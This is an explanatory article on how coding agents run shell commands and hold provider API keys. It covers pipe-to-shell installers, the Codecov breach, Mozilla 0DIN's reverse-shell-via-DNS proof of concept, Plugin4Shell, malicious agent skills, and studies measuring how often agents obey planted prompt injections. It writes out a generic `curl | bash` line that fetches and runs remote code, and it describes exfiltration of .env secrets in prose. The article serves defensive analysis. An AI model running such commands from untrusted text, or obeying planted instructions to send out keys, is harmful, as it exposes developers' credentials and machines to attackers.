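# Pipe-to-shell commands and provider API key leaks in coding agents

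## How coding agents run commands and hold provider keys

A coding agent is a program in which a language model proposes actions, such as editing a file or running a shell command, and ordinary software carries them out. Examples include Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. A developer might ask the agent in plain language to fix a failing test, and the agent then installs packages, edits code and reruns the tests until they pass. The agent normally runs with that developer's permissions, and it needs a credential for the company that hosts the model.

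Two security problems arise from this arrangement. The agent may run a pipe-to-shell command, which downloads text from the internet and runs it in a shell before anyone has read it. Outsiders may also get hold of the provider API key, the secret string that a company such as Anthropic, OpenAI or Google uses to identify and bill a customer. Both problems are older than coding agents, but an agent runs commands in the same user account that holds the key, so a single pipe-to-shell command can leak it.

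### The agent loop

A model can only propose shell commands, as OpenAI notes in describing its API for agents. Separate software, which developers call the harness, runs the commands, holds the model's permissions and returns the output.

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how the Codex harness first assembles a prompt, the full text that the model will work from. The prompt contains general instructions, a list of tools the model may request, a note on which folders the agent may write to and when it must ask the user, the current directory, and finally the user's message. One of the tools is a shell, whose definition has fields for the command, the directory to run it in and a time limit.

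The model then responds with either a message to the user or a request for a tool. In Bolin's example, the user wants an architecture diagram added to the README, the file that introduces the project, and the model requests `cat README.md`, which prints that file. The harness runs the command, appends the request and the output to the prompt, and queries the model again, so the model can use the README's contents to propose a next step. The cycle repeats until the model writes a message to the user instead of requesting a tool. Bolin mentions that a single turn might contain hundreds of tool calls.

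The harness can check a command after the model requests it and before it runs. Anthropic's *How Claude Code works* lists several settings for this check. In manual mode, the harness asks the user before file edits and shell commands. A looser mode allows edits and common file operations without asking, but still asks about other commands. In auto mode, a classifier, which is a model that judges whether a proposed action may run, reviews most actions in the background. Recent versions of Claude Code start interactive terminal sessions in auto mode.

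According to NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*, asking the user for approval is the most common control, but developers who must keep returning to the window to approve actions begin to approve them without looking.

Once a command passes the check, it usually runs under the developer's user account. Anthropic says Claude Code can run any command that its user could run from the same terminal, including build tools and system utilities. Unless the harness adds a sandbox, in which the operating system or a container restricts file and network access, the agent can use `cat` to read any file the developer can read.

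### A pipe-to-shell command, piece by piece

The usual form of the command is short:

`curl -fsSL https://example.com/install.sh | bash`

- `curl` is a program that fetches whatever a web address returns and prints it.
- `-f` makes curl stop with an error if the server reports one, such as a missing page. Without it, the text of the error page would travel on to the shell.
- `-s` silences the progress display and the error messages, and `-S` brings the error messages back.
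- `-L` makes curl follow redirects, so the text can come from a different address than the one in the command.
- `https://example.com/install.sh` is the address of a script, a text file of shell commands. Nothing in the command fixes what the file contains. It contains whatever the server sends at that moment.
- `|`, the pipe, connects the output of the program on its left to the input of the program on its right.
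- `bash` is a shell, a program that runs commands. Because the line gives it no file to open, it takes its commands from its input, which here is the downloaded text.

Piping curl's output into bash runs the script without saving it. *Practical Agentic Software Supply Chain Security* (Monperrus, 2026) points out that this leaves no opportunity to inspect the script or compare it with a known fingerprint. Bash runs commands as they arrive, so the first lines may take effect before the last have downloaded.

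The model in an agent loop therefore does not see the script either. Its request contains only the one line above, and the prompt then receives the script's output, which is whatever the person who wrote the script wanted it to print.

Reading the script in a browser first doesn't guarantee that curl will download the same one. Browsers and curl send the server different User-Agent headers, and the security company OnSecurity shows that a two-line program on the server is enough to send a harmless script to the browser and a malicious one to curl. Its example of a real command that people run this way is the NodeSource installer for Node.js, a popular system for running JavaScript. That command runs the script in bash with administrator rights and an option that preserves the user's environment variables.

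Fetching the script with curl and reading the saved copy removes the difference in User-Agent, but a server may still be able to distinguish a download saved to disk from one piped to a shell. Ecosyste.ms' *curl-bash-attack* describes a demonstration program that detects a piped run from the timing of the download, based on an idea published in 2016. A clean saved copy therefore doesn't show that a piped download would also be clean. Running the saved file is the only way to be sure that the script being run is the one that was read.

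### Why projects still publish piped installers

Reputable projects publish such lines all the same, among them the makers of coding agents. For unattended installation of Codex, OpenAI's *Environment variables* gives this command:

`curl -fsSL https://chatgpt.com/codex/install.sh | CODEX_NON_INTERACTIVE=1 sh`

Pipe-to-shell installers are convenient because one command works on a new machine whose owner hasn't yet chosen a package manager. The script can detect the system and download the right build. It also suits automated machines, where nobody is present to click through an installer. If the publisher corrects the script, everyone who runs the command afterwards gets the correction.

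Piping an installer into a shell arguably adds little risk, as long as the server delivers what the publisher wrote. Anyone who installs a program is about to run its publisher's code anyway, and an installer downloaded from the same publisher over an encrypted connection requires no more trust than the program itself.

Codecov sells a service that measures how much of a program its tests exercise. Its customers uploaded their measurements with a script called the Bash Uploader, which Codecov's documentation told them to download and pipe to bash on every build. According to Codecov's *Bash Uploader Security Update* (2021), an intruder altered the script in early 2021, using a credential extracted through an error in the company's process for building Docker images, the packaged file systems from which containers start. The intruder added one command, which sent the environment variables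 of the machine running the script and the address of the code repository to a server outside Codecov.

The altered script was live for 108 separate periods between 31 January and its discovery on 1 April. CISA's *Codecov Releases New Detections for Supply Chain Compromise* (2021), an alert from the US government's cybersecurity agency, gives the same dates. The change also reached customers who had never typed the command, because Codecov's ready-made integrations for GitHub and two other build services used the same uploader, according to the company's post-mortem.

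A customer found the intrusion by computing the checksum of the downloaded script, a short fingerprint that changes if the file changes, and comparing it with the one Codecov published on GitHub. Monperrus doubts the value of checksums because few projects provide them and an attacker who controls the site that publishes them can replace them too. The Codecov case partly supports his view. The checksum helped because it was on a different site from the script and somebody checked it, but by then two months had passed.

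### What an agent changes

The Codecov incident did not involve a coding agent. Monperrus, a researcher at the KTH Royal Institute of Technology in Stockholm, argued in June 2026 that agents change the old danger of pipe-to-shell commands in three ways. He also proposes a rule that blocks piped commands before they run, but his argument about the danger does not depend on that rule.

A coding agent working by itself may run dozens of shell commands for a single task without a human reviewing each one. A person who pastes an installer line into a terminal at least decides whether to run it.

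Prompt injection is text planted in material the model reads, written so that the model treats it as an instruction. It is possible because the loop puts command output, such as the contents of a file after `cat README.md`, into the same prompt as the user's request. Bolin describes how each message in the prompt has a role that indicates how much weight its content should have, in descending order from system through developer and user to assistant. But roles don't guarantee that the model will ignore an instruction in the README, because it generates its next request from the whole prompt.

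Security researchers call this attack indirect because the attacker never talks to the model and only leaves text where the model will read it. NVIDIA considers indirect attacks the primary threat to coding agents and says the text can arrive through malicious repositories and pull requests, commit history, agent instruction files, and responses from external tool servers.

Monperrus gives the example of a package whose README advises the reader to run one more piped command for best performance. An agent that reads the file while setting up the project may run the command word for word. He presents this as a possible attack and does not report how often it succeeds. The example is plausible because honest projects put the same kind of command in their installation instructions, and an agent that refused them all would fail at ordinary work. The planted command differs from an honest one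 in who controls the server, which the agent cannot learn from the README.

His third difference is that the agent acts under the developer's credentials and file permissions, so a compromised script runs as the developer rather than in an isolated sandbox. By itself, this seems the least novel of the three, because a developer who pastes the line by hand also runs it from their own account. With an agent, however, the choice of command may trace back to a sentence that a stranger wrote in a file the developer never opened.

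### Where provider keys live

Each web request Codex makes for a model response includes an authorisation header, which typically carries a key or a login token. The harness therefore has to find this credential on the machine, commonly in one of three places.

The first is an environment variable, a named value that a process holds and, by default, copies to every program it starts. A developer might set one called `OPENAI_API_KEY` in a terminal, or in a file that the terminal loads at startup. Unless one of the processes is set up to withhold it, the terminal passes the key to the coding agent, the agent passes it to the shell it opens for a command, and the shell passes it to each program in that command. A program cannot alter the variables of the process that started it, but a malicious program can read the key from its own copy.

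OpenAI's installer line above uses the same mechanism for a harmless purpose. Putting `CODEX_NON_INTERACTIVE=1` before `sh` sets a variable in the environment of that one shell, and the install script reads it and skips its questions. If the developer exported an API key earlier in the same terminal, that environment also contains the key.

Many projects also keep secrets in a file named `.env`, a plain list of names and values that an application loads when it starts. NVIDIA mentions `.env` files with API tokens as something typically found in an agent's current workspace. The file is in the project folder, where the agent has legitimate reasons to read files.

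The third place is login files, which a coding agent uses to remember users who sign in through an account. According to OpenAI, Codex keeps its authentication data by default in the folder `~/.codex` in the user's home directory, alongside its settings, logs and sessions. File permissions can keep other people's accounts on the computer out of such a folder, but they don't stop another program running under the same account from reading it.

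Codex accepts a key for a single unattended run through the variable `CODEX_API_KEY`. When the automated job runs code that the repository controls, OpenAI advises setting the variable only for the Codex command, not for the whole job. Every step inherits a job-wide variable, including test scripts that an outside contributor may have edited. Setting it for one command limits it to Codex and the processes Codex starts, and some harnesses filter the environment again when they start those processes.

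### What a stolen key is worth

Anyone who has a provider API key can use it. If someone steals a key, they can use the models for free or sell access to them, and the provider bills the account the key belongs to.

In February 2026, a software firm of three developers in Mexico that normally spent about $180 a month on Google's services ran up a bill of $82,314 in two days. Techzine's *Misused Gemini API key results in sky-high AI costs for startup* reports that most of it went on text and images from Google's Gemini models. One of the developers posted the figures on Reddit. He said Google first responded that customers are responsible for guarding their own keys. Tom's Hardware's *Gemini API key thief racks up $82,314 in charges* adds that he expected the bill to bankrupt the company if Google insisted on it. The same article says some Google customers can set quotas on requests, while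 those on Google Cloud can set budget alerts, which notify them when spending passes a certain sum.

Larger organisations have lost more. Google Threat Intelligence Group's *The Rise of LLMJacking* (2026), published on 2 November with Google's Mandiant incident responders, covers the criminal trade in stolen access to language models. Help Net Security's *Stolen AI access leaves companies with cloud bills* (2026) cites its findings that some victims were charged more than $100,000 in a single day, and that totals reached up to $1 million before the attackers lost access. In one case, the thieves made over 500,000 calls to models in less than eight hours to supply Jet Night, a resale service that offered unlimited use for about $60 a month. A comparable legitimate subscription would cost between $100 and $250.

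Some groups now specialise in breaking in, while others run the gateways that pool and resell the access. Google expects criminals to favour this business over hijacking computers to mine cryptocurrency, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *LLMJacking is Costing Some Businesses Up to $1m*. In line with that forecast, average prices for AI accounts on underground forums more than doubled during 2026, as Infor.pl's *Ktoś używa AI na koszt twojej firmy. Ekspert Google ostrzega przed LLMjackingiem* (2026) reports from Google's research, and demand is much higher for company accounts than private ones.

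These sums measure what access is worth to a thief. They are poor evidence of how often coding agents leak it, because Help Net Security notes that most of the intruders got in with stolen cloud credentials: service account keys, GitHub access tokens, or tokens for active sessions. Developers' machines often hold such credentials too, where the same commands can reach them.

### How the two risks join

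If an agent runs the earlier piped command without a sandbox and the script is malicious, the script starts as a child process of the harness and inherits its environment variables, including any key the harness has not removed. It runs under the developer's account, so it can also open the `.env` file and the login folder. The network must be open, because the script was just downloaded over it. The attacker can therefore steal the key without exploiting a flaw in the operating system or the agent. The script only has to read a variable and send it to a web address, and legitimate scripts routinely do both. The Codecov intruder did so with a single added command.

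The harness can inspect a tool call and its arguments before they run, as NVIDIA explains, but it can't see what another process does after taking control. A permission prompt shows the user an address and the word `bash`, but not the script's contents. If a malicious script also installs the promised software, the model receives output that looks like a successful installation, and the agent continues its task.

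Keys also leak without a piped script. An agent looking for a configuration error may print the `.env` file. The output becomes part of the prompt sent to the model provider, and Claude Code also writes every tool result to a plain-text session file on the developer's disk. A key can also end up in the code and be published with it. GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) counted 1,275,105 leaked secrets for AI services in 2025, 81 percent more than the year before. That category includes databases and other supporting services as well as model providers, and the total does not separate agents' mistakes from people's.

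A key that its owner published deliberately can become dangerous later. Techzine reports that the firm Truffle Security found 2,863 active Google keys on the public internet that could send requests to Gemini. Many were originally identifiers for services such as Google Maps, meant to be visible in a web page's source, and gained access to the models when someone later enabled Gemini for the same project. Thieves collect exposed keys systematically. One group described by Help Net Security took keys from public GitHub repositories and tested each with requests too small to trigger the owner's alerts.

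## The Mozilla 0DIN test: a repository that led an agent to run remote text

On 25 June 2026, two researchers at 0DIN, Mozilla's bug bounty programme for AI systems, published *Clone This Repo and I Own Your Machine* (Hall and Engelbrecht, 2026). They tested whether an attacker who controls only a public GitHub repository could, without putting malicious code in it, run code on the computer of anyone who opens the repository with Claude Code. While setting up an ordinary-looking project in their test, Claude Code gave an outsider a shell on the developer's machine.

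The harness can inspect a `curl ... | bash` line because it appears in the model's request. In this test, however, the text that bash ran came from a script that the model's command started indirectly.

The test was a demonstration, not an attack on the public, and Help Net Security's *Mozilla warns of indirect prompt injection risk in AI coding agents* calls it a proof of concept. Hall and Engelbrecht describe a single chain of events that worked, but they do not give the Claude Code version, the permission mode or the number of runs. Their post therefore shows that the chain is possible, but measuring its success rate would require experiments that repeat such attacks many times.

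### From a setup error to a shell

The developer copies the repository link and asks Claude Code to get the project running. Claude Code reads the setup notes into its prompt. The steps are to install the required packages, then run an initialisation command once before anything else. 0DIN classifies the attack as indirect prompt injection, but the notes contain no instruction to ignore the user or keep a secret, and many legitimate projects have similar notes.

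Claude Code installs the packages and tries to use the program, which stops with an error. The error message gives a command for initialising the project, and the harness adds the message to the prompt, where it matches the setup notes. The prompt contains no sign that the attacker wrote the package to fail on first use so that the fix would lead to a script. Plenty of legitimate software also stops with an error until it is configured, and a user who asks an agent to get a project running expects it to read errors and apply the documented fix.

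The model then requests the initialisation command, which is a short call to a Python package. Any check that looks only at the command can inspect only that call. In manual mode, the permission prompt would show the user a command that matched the project's own instructions. A guard rule, which checks a command before it runs, would find no download piped into a shell.

The call runs a shell script elsewhere in the repository. The script was on the developer's disk, so the model could have read it first. 0DIN counts the script as one of the steps between what Claude Code evaluated and the attacker's shell.

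The script looks up what appears to be a configuration value in DNS, the system that translates names such as example.com into numeric addresses, and passes it to bash as a command. DNS also lets a domain's owner attach free text to a name, in a TXT record. Email systems rely on these records, according to Tom's Hardware's *AI coding agents can be tricked into installing malware*, so a script that looks one up doesn't seem odd. Attackers have used TXT records before. According to DomainTools, a company that studies internet domains, they can hold entire malicious programs, and businesses often monitor DNS less well than their firewalls.

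Neither the model nor the developer saw the contents of the record. The script printed two harmless lines, ending with a message that the environment was ready. To the model, this output looked like a successful repair.

### What the attacker's shell could reach

The text in the record opened a reverse shell, which is a shell on the victim's machine that connects out to the attacker's server and takes commands from it. The attacker can then look around the machine and decide what to take, instead of relying on a script written in advance.

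The shell ran under the developer's own account, so it had access to `.env` files and login folders. 0DIN says it also exposed every secret in the environment, such as an Anthropic API key, an Amazon cloud key and a GitHub token.

Replacing a stolen key might not end the intrusion. Before the shell closes, the attacker can install a backdoor, schedule a job to run later, or add an SSH key for logging in remotely. A new provider key stored on the same machine would then be exposed too.

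The researchers suggest that an attacker could spread the repository through a job posting, a tutorial or a Slack message. They write that one link would hit everyone who opens it with Claude Code, but a single successful attack chain can't support that claim.

### Why reviewing the repository doesn't reveal the payload

Code reviewers and security scanners examine the files in a repository, so they could not find the reverse shell, which the attacker kept in the DNS record. The attacker could also replace it at any time without making a commit, so a repository that had passed review could later run different code even though its files had not changed.

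0DIN's claims that no scanner would ever catch the attack and that every file in the repository passes review seem too strong. The payload was not in the repository, but the script contained the line that ran the fetched text, and 0DIN calls that line "the whole trick". A reviewer who opened the script could object to the line without knowing what the record contained, and a scanner could flag any line that runs text from the network. 0DIN does not name any scanner it tried. However, legitimate installers contain similar lines, so a reviewer who saw a warning would still have to decide whether to trust the server.

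The researchers' better point is that the attack divides the evidence. A scanner finds a DNS lookup in the script, network monitoring records a name lookup, and the agent sees a documented setup step. Recognising the attack requires connecting all three, but these checks normally run separately.

### Whether an agent can show what a command will execute

0DIN says agents should show what a setup command will run, including the contents of any script it starts and anything the script fetches. It also advises developers to treat setup instructions in unfamiliar repositories as untrusted code, whatever their AI tool recommends.

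In this test, a harness could have followed the call from the Python package to the script and displayed the script before running it. This is harder with larger programs, which may start hundreds of files and may determine which ones only while running. Users who approve short commands without reading them are also unlikely to read hundreds of files.

Showing what the script fetches is a different problem, because the text isn't on the machine until the script requests it. The harness could preview the DNS record, but the attacker could change it before the script runs. As with a piped installer, the harness would have to save a copy, show it, and run that same copy. It can do this when the model requests a download directly, but when a script does the fetching, the harness would have to intercept the request, hold the reply for approval, and repeat the process if running the reply triggers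 another fetch.

Another approach is to run the code in a sandbox first and watch what it does. Researchers at the Hong Kong University of Science and Technology built SkillDetonate to do this for skills, which are bundles of plain-English instructions, scripts and other files that an agent loads for a particular kind of task. The tool labels sensitive data when a skill reads it and follows the label through files, programs and network connections. Help Net Security's *Malicious AI agent skills can slip past the scanners* (2026) reports that SkillDetonate caught 97 percent of attacks in a synthetic benchmark and 87 percent of real malicious skills, with false alarms in about 2 percent of cases. Scanners that only read the files did much worse, since malicious skills disguised in one particular way got past every scanner more than 90 percent of the time.

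SkillDetonate can catch payloads that appear only at run time, as in the 0DIN case. But it runs once, at installation, so it would miss the attack if the attacker's server returned something harmless during the test and a reverse shell a week later.

So 0DIN's advice works fully for files already on the disk but only partly for text that arrives later. An agent could still report that a script is about to run unread text from an outside server. That is less than 0DIN asks for, but it would give the developer a reason to stop. Network limits could also help, whether or not anyone reads the text. Tom's Hardware suggests that a company with very tightly controlled network access could catch the attack.

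### Plugin4Shell: a reviewed version that agents did not verify

Plugins are add-ons that a coding agent installs from a marketplace. A Claude Code plugin gets full access to the user's terminal, local files and environment variables, according to *Securing Claude Code plug-ins* (Kapner, 2026), a guide from the software company Red Hat.

Marketplaces use pinning to stop a plugin from changing after review. Someone reviews the plugin at one commit, and the marketplace records that commit's hash, a 40-character string that identifies the snapshot of the code. The agent is supposed to install only that snapshot.

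On 17 September 2026, the security company AIR disclosed in *Plugin4Shell* that Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Google's Gemini CLI all requested the pinned commit without checking that they had received it. Someone who controlled a plugin's repository could exploit an ambiguity in how git looks up names to make the agent install different code while the pin still appeared intact.

This required no action from the user. Help Net Security's *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched* (2026) explains that Claude Code and Codex update plugins in the background by default. When the marketplace moved the pin to a newer commit, the agent repeated the flawed step, and the attacker's code could reach a plugin that was already installed. An attacker could publish a useful plugin and turn it malicious later, or take over the repository of a plugin that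 people trusted.

AIR built working exploits against all four agents in May and told the vendors in June. *Plugin4Shell*, a news report by Constantin (2026) for The Next Web, describes a one-line fix in which the agent compares the fetched code with the pin and stops if they differ. Anthropic made the fix in version 2.1.179 of Claude Code, and OpenAI in version 0.146.0 of Codex. As of 21 September, Microsoft had not released a fix for Copilot, and Google did not plan one for Gemini CLI, which it is retiring in favour of a newer agent.

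GitHub replied that its platform rejects the kind of name that the attack on Copilot needs. IlSoftware.it's *Plugin4Shell, falla zero-click negli agenti AI* reports AIR's response that Copilot also accepts repositories hosted elsewhere. The researchers say a marketplace can't fully fix the problem, because the agent resolves the pin on the user's machine. AIR has a commercial interest in the subject, since it sells a marketplace and a filter and says that customers using both were unaffected. However, the fixes from Anthropic and OpenAI support its basic finding.

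In both Plugin4Shell and the 0DIN test, the code that ran differed from the code available for review. Plugin4Shell was easier to fix because a reviewed version existed and the agent could check the code against its hash. Nobody had reviewed the text in 0DIN's DNS record, and an agent that correctly verified the repository's hash would still have run it.

AIR had demonstrated this limit in June 2026 with a skill that claimed to build web pages using a Google design tool. The skill sent agents to a web address on a domain that AIR owned. The address first led to Google's real documentation, but AIR replaced the page once many people had installed the skill. According to the German article *Fake-Skill umgeht Scanner*, scanners from Cisco, NVIDIA and the marketplace skills.sh had passed the skill because they analysed only the submitted package and not the page it linked to.

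The new page could have told agents to download and run a script, but AIR used it only to collect users' email addresses. The company says the skill reached more than 26,000 agents, which the German article describes as unconfirmed. In *Anatomy of a Malicious AI Skill*, Hoppe (2026) traces the skill's route through public GitHub records, including the pull request that submitted it and the review. He concludes that the trick depends on review and execution happening at different times.

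### Malicious skills in actual use

Criminals have already used setup instructions that fetch and run code. One campaign, ClawHavoc, planted malicious skills on ClawHub, a public registry for the personal AI agent OpenClaw. According to SC Media, Oren Yomtov of Koi Security examined all 2,857 skills there and found 341 malicious ones, 335 of which seemed to belong to that campaign.

Yomtov told The Hacker News (2026) that the skills had professional-looking documentation with a "Prerequisites" section that listed something else to install first. On macOS, users had to copy an installation script from a website and paste it into the terminal. That script fetched and ran a second one to deliver Atomic Stealer, a data-stealing program. According to Help Net Security, the stealer took browser credentials, stored passwords, SSH keys and cryptocurrency wallets.

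It is less clear how often an agent ran these steps itself. The Hacker News and *ClawHavoc*, an analysis by the Chinese security company Antiy, describe instructions to the user, while Help Net Security says the files contained instructions for the agent to fetch and run the stealer. Both could be true, since a user and an agent may read the same file. *Exploring the Emerging Threats of the Agent Skill Ecosystem* (2026) describes the agent's part more directly. It confirms 76 malicious skills, and the warning signs it lists include instructions for the agent to install malware linked from other sites. Eight of the 76 were still available on ClawHub when the paper was published.

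*Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (2026) classified 82 skills that hid a harmful purpose behind a harmless one, and 34 of them (41 percent) were malicious installers. Some of the installers used a `curl | bash` line as a setup step. One posed as a coding agent that worked with several popular developer tools and told users to download a "driver package".

*MalSkillBench* (2026) explains why a setup step is a good disguise for an attack, based on 703 malicious skills collected on ClawHub. A skill runs while the agent works on a task for its user, so an attacker can present a harmful action as progress on that task. For example, reading credentials can be presented as part of setting up a login, and running a command as initialising a helper program. 0DIN's project used the same disguise. However, most of the 703 skills come from a few large campaigns, so they are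 a poor guide to the full range of attacks.

Estimates of how common malicious skills are differ widely. Koi's count was about 12 percent of ClawHub at the time, and most of it came from a single campaign. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (2026) confirmed 157 malicious skills among 98,380, or less than 0.2 percent, according to the totals in *SKILLLITE* (2026). That study covered more than one registry and counted only skills whose malicious behaviour had been verified. Its definition of malicious behaviour includes downloading and running outside code.

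Help Net Security's *Thousands of malicious AI skills found capable of stealing data, running malware* (2026) reports that the security company ESET had counted more than 3,000 malicious skills by May 2026, up from about 600 in March. Over the same period, the number of skills ESET scanned rose from 60,000 to almost 900,000. The malicious share therefore fell from about 1 percent to about 0.3 percent, and much of the increase may be due to ESET scanning more skills.

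Attackers have also changed skills after people installed them, much as AIR did in its test. TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever* describes a campaign that Zenity Labs found on skills.sh. The attackers copied existing skills under similar names and kept the copies harmless until they had gathered installations. They then added instructions that told agents to collect and send out secrets such as SSH keys, cloud credentials and environment files. One family of these skills had more than 1.7 million installations, but that total includes repeat installations, so it isn't the number of victims. Vercel, which runs skills.sh, and Microsoft removed the skills that Zenity identified, but anyone who had already installed one must delete it by hand.

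## Experiments on how often agents obey planted commands

A model that opens a web page during a task should use the page as information and ignore any commands in it. Developers rely on role markers in the prompt for this. The markers show the source of each piece of text, and the model is trained not to follow commands in text marked as tool output.

The 0DIN test showed that agents can obey planted commands, but not how often they do. Researchers who have repeated similar attacks hundreds of times report success rates from zero to 84 percent. Most of that variation comes from differences in what they tested and how they counted successes.

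### Why a model obeys text it should only read

In *Prompt Injection Attacks on Agentic Coding Assistants*, Maloyan and Namiot (2026) review 78 studies and attribute prompt injection to the fact that language models, unlike ordinary software, process instructions and data along the same pathway.

Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, propose a more specific cause, which they call role confusion. They argue that a model judges the source of text mainly by how it sounds, so a command on a web page can gain the user's authority by sounding like the user.

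The researchers' evidence comes from probes, which are small classifiers trained on the numbers a model computes while processing text. They wrapped the same passages of web text in each role's markers and trained a probe to tell which markers surrounded a passage. Because the passages were identical, the probe could learn only the markers' effect on those numbers.

The researchers then applied the probes to messages that real people had sent to chatbots. With the correct markers, the probes rated these messages 84 to almost 100 percent likely to be user text on average, depending on the model. When the researchers relabelled the same messages as tool output, the probability stayed between 76 and 88 percent. It should have dropped close to zero if the models relied on the markers.

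A model can resist a planted command, however it is worded, because it identifies the command as coming from a web page. It can also resist because a request to send out secrets resembles a familiar kind of attack, but then an unfamiliar wording can succeed. Ye and colleagues conclude that current models rely on this resemblance.

### Planted requests on 100 web pages

The same researchers tested six OpenAI models, ranging from the small open model gpt-oss-20b to GPT-5. Each model ran in a simple agent loop with a bash shell as its only tool and a `.env` file in its workspace. The user asked the agent to read a web page and summarise it in a few sentences. In the transcript shown in the paper, the user also warned the agent not to carry out malicious commands from the page.

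The pages were 100 Wikipedia articles, each in two versions. One version contained a plain request, worded as if the user had written it, to find the `.env` file and send its contents to an outside server. The other added a paragraph meant to make the model trust the request. Anyone viewing either version in a browser would have seen only the article.

Five of the six models acted on the plain request in 0 to 2 percent of runs, while gpt-oss-20b did so in 26 percent. With the added paragraph, the rates for all six models rose to between 56 and 70 percent.

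Another model, Gemini 2.5 Pro, judged from the record of each run whether the attack had worked. The paper's main text defines success as uploading the file, but its appendix also counts attempts where the upload failed. The figures therefore measure how often the models obeyed, and somewhat fewer files may have reached the server.

In a test with only the plain request, five of these models would have appeared nearly immune. The commands and pages were the same in both versions, so the added text must have caused the difference between 2 percent and 56 percent. A low rate in such a test shows resistance only to the wordings tested.

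The researchers also checked whether role confusion predicts which attacks succeed. They kept one command fixed, varied the text around it in 212 ways, and ran 1,000 attempts with the resulting pages. For each attempt, a probe measured how strongly the model represented the command as user text. The agent tried to send the file in 2 percent of attempts in the group with the lowest scores and 70 percent in the group with the highest.

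This pattern fits the proposed cause but does not quite establish it, since wording that sounds more like a user could also be more persuasive for some other reason. A separate experiment with harmful chat requests is better evidence. When the researchers reworded their stronger attack text but kept its argument, the attack's success rate fell from 61 to 10 percent, so the argument alone evidently had little effect.

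Probes require access to a model's internals, so the researchers could use them only on four open models, the largest with about 120 billion parameters. GPT-5 behaved the same way, but the study can't show that the internal cause is the same. Ye and colleagues expect further training to teach models to recognise this particular attack, but they argue that other wordings would still work until models can reliably track where text came from.

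### Planted commands in coding rules

Some files are harder to classify than a web page because the agent is supposed to obey them. A coding rules file tells an agent how to write code for a project, such as which libraries and naming conventions to use, and developers often download one that somebody else wrote. In *Your AI, My Shell*, Liu, Zhao and colleagues (2025) planted commands in such files and tested Cursor and GitHub Copilot, two code editors with built-in coding agents.

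The test system, AIShellJack, contains 314 payloads, planted instructions that each aim at one malicious action. The payloads cover 70 techniques from MITRE ATT&CK, a public catalogue of real attackers' methods. The researchers adapted the payloads from an open-source collection of commands for testing security software and removed words such as "steal" and "adversary" from the descriptions. Most payloads described an action in plain English and left the agent to work out the command.

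For each test, a script opened one of five open-source projects and the altered rules file in a fresh copy of the editor. The script then prompted the agent to reorganise the code according to the rules and logged every terminal command for the next three minutes. The researchers had set both editors to run commands without asking the user. They ran each test once.

With Cursor's Auto setting, which lets Cursor choose the model, the attacks succeeded in 66.9 to 84.1 percent of tests, depending on the project. Credential-access payloads, which try to obtain passwords and keys, succeeded in 133 of 195 tests (68.2 percent). They included searching files and shell history for secrets, extracting the operating system's stored passwords and recording keystrokes.

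The researchers compared other combinations of editor and model on one of the five projects, a search application written in TypeScript:

| Editor and model | All 314 payloads | Credential access (39 payloads) | Credentials in files (6 of the 39) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cursor, Auto | 83.4% | 31 | 6 |
| Cursor, Claude 4 Sonnet | 69.1% | 32 | 6 |
| Cursor, Gemini 2.5 Pro | 73.9% | 25 | 3 |
| Copilot, Claude 4 Sonnet | 52.2% | 16 | 3 |
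| Copilot, Gemini 2.5 Pro | 41.1% | 16 | 6 |

The paper also gives 76.8 percent for Cursor with Gemini, but only 73.9 fits its breakdown of outcomes.

Claude 4 Sonnet carried out 32 of the credential payloads in Cursor and 16 in Copilot. Since the model was the same, the harnesses probably account for much of the difference, although each test was run only once and chance may have contributed. The overall rate is also a poor guide to the risk for a provider key. Copilot with Gemini resisted more payloads than any other combination, but it carried out all six payloads for finding credentials in files, the category closest to an agent reading a `.env` file.

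AIShellJack treats exfiltration, which means sending stolen data to the attacker, as a separate category from collecting credentials. Its nine exfiltration payloads succeeded in 25 of 45 tests with Cursor in Auto mode. The 68.2 percent is therefore the rate at which the agent began to collect credentials, and the share of keys that would have reached an attacker could be lower.

The study's scoring was generous to the attacker. A program compared the commands the agent ran with the command the payload should have produced. It counted a success if at least a fifth of the expected words matched, or if a matching command went beyond routine setup such as creating a folder. The command did not have to achieve its purpose.

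Because such a loose rule could inflate the rates, two of the researchers checked 339 of the 2,826 results by hand. They agreed with the program in 99.1 percent of cases and found that 89.6 percent of the successful attacks had carried out the whole intended action. If that share held for the project with the highest rate, counting only complete attacks would lower its rate from 84 percent to about 75 percent.

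Wording also mattered in a smaller trial with 20 payloads. The standard version succeeded 15 times, but versions with parts of the text around the command removed succeeded once or not at all. Changing the user's request had little effect.

Automatic approval made the attacks easier, but Liu and colleagues justify using it on the grounds that it is common practice among developers. A variant that did not need terminal access still left the planted action in the project's code in 277 of 314 tests.

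### The Trajectory Labs evaluation

The lowest rates come from a test of newer agents. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) announces that auto mode, which uses a classifier, will become the default on most plans. To support the change, Anthropic published a study of how poorly people review commands and an evaluation it commissioned from an outside firm, Trajectory Labs.

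Trajectory Labs tested versions of Claude Code and Codex from July 2026. It wrote 72 indirect prompt injection scenarios, which it withheld from Anthropic, and ran each one 10 times for every combination of model and mode, for a total of 720 attempts per combination. Both agents used the same browser tool, which Trajectory Labs had built. An attack counted as successful if it would have caused irreversible harm outside the test, for example by sending out sensitive data, committing financial fraud or phishing for credentials.

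None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5 in auto mode, and Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 had the same result. In Codex's Auto-review mode, 42 of 720 attempts (5.83 percent) succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. In Full Access mode, which lacks that review, 137 of 720 (19.03 percent) succeeded.

Both Codex tests used the same scenarios and model, so the drop from 137 to 42 is fairly good evidence that Auto-review helps. The zero for Claude is much weaker evidence that auto mode helps. When Trajectory Labs ran Anthropic's latest models with permission checks bypassed, an average of only 0.09 percent of attempts succeeded. If that average covers the same three models, that is two successes in 2,160 attempts. Almost every attack failed even without the classifier, so it had very little to block.

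A result of zero also leaves the true failure rate somewhat uncertain. If the 720 attempts were independent, an agent with a true rate of 0.4 percent would still have about a one in twenty chance of no failures. But ten runs of the same scenario are likely to end alike. If they always did, the 720 attempts would count as only 72, and an agent with a true rate of 4 percent would have about the same chance of no failures. The 42 successes against Codex may also include repeats of the same scenario, so they could come from as few as five scenarios or as many as 42.

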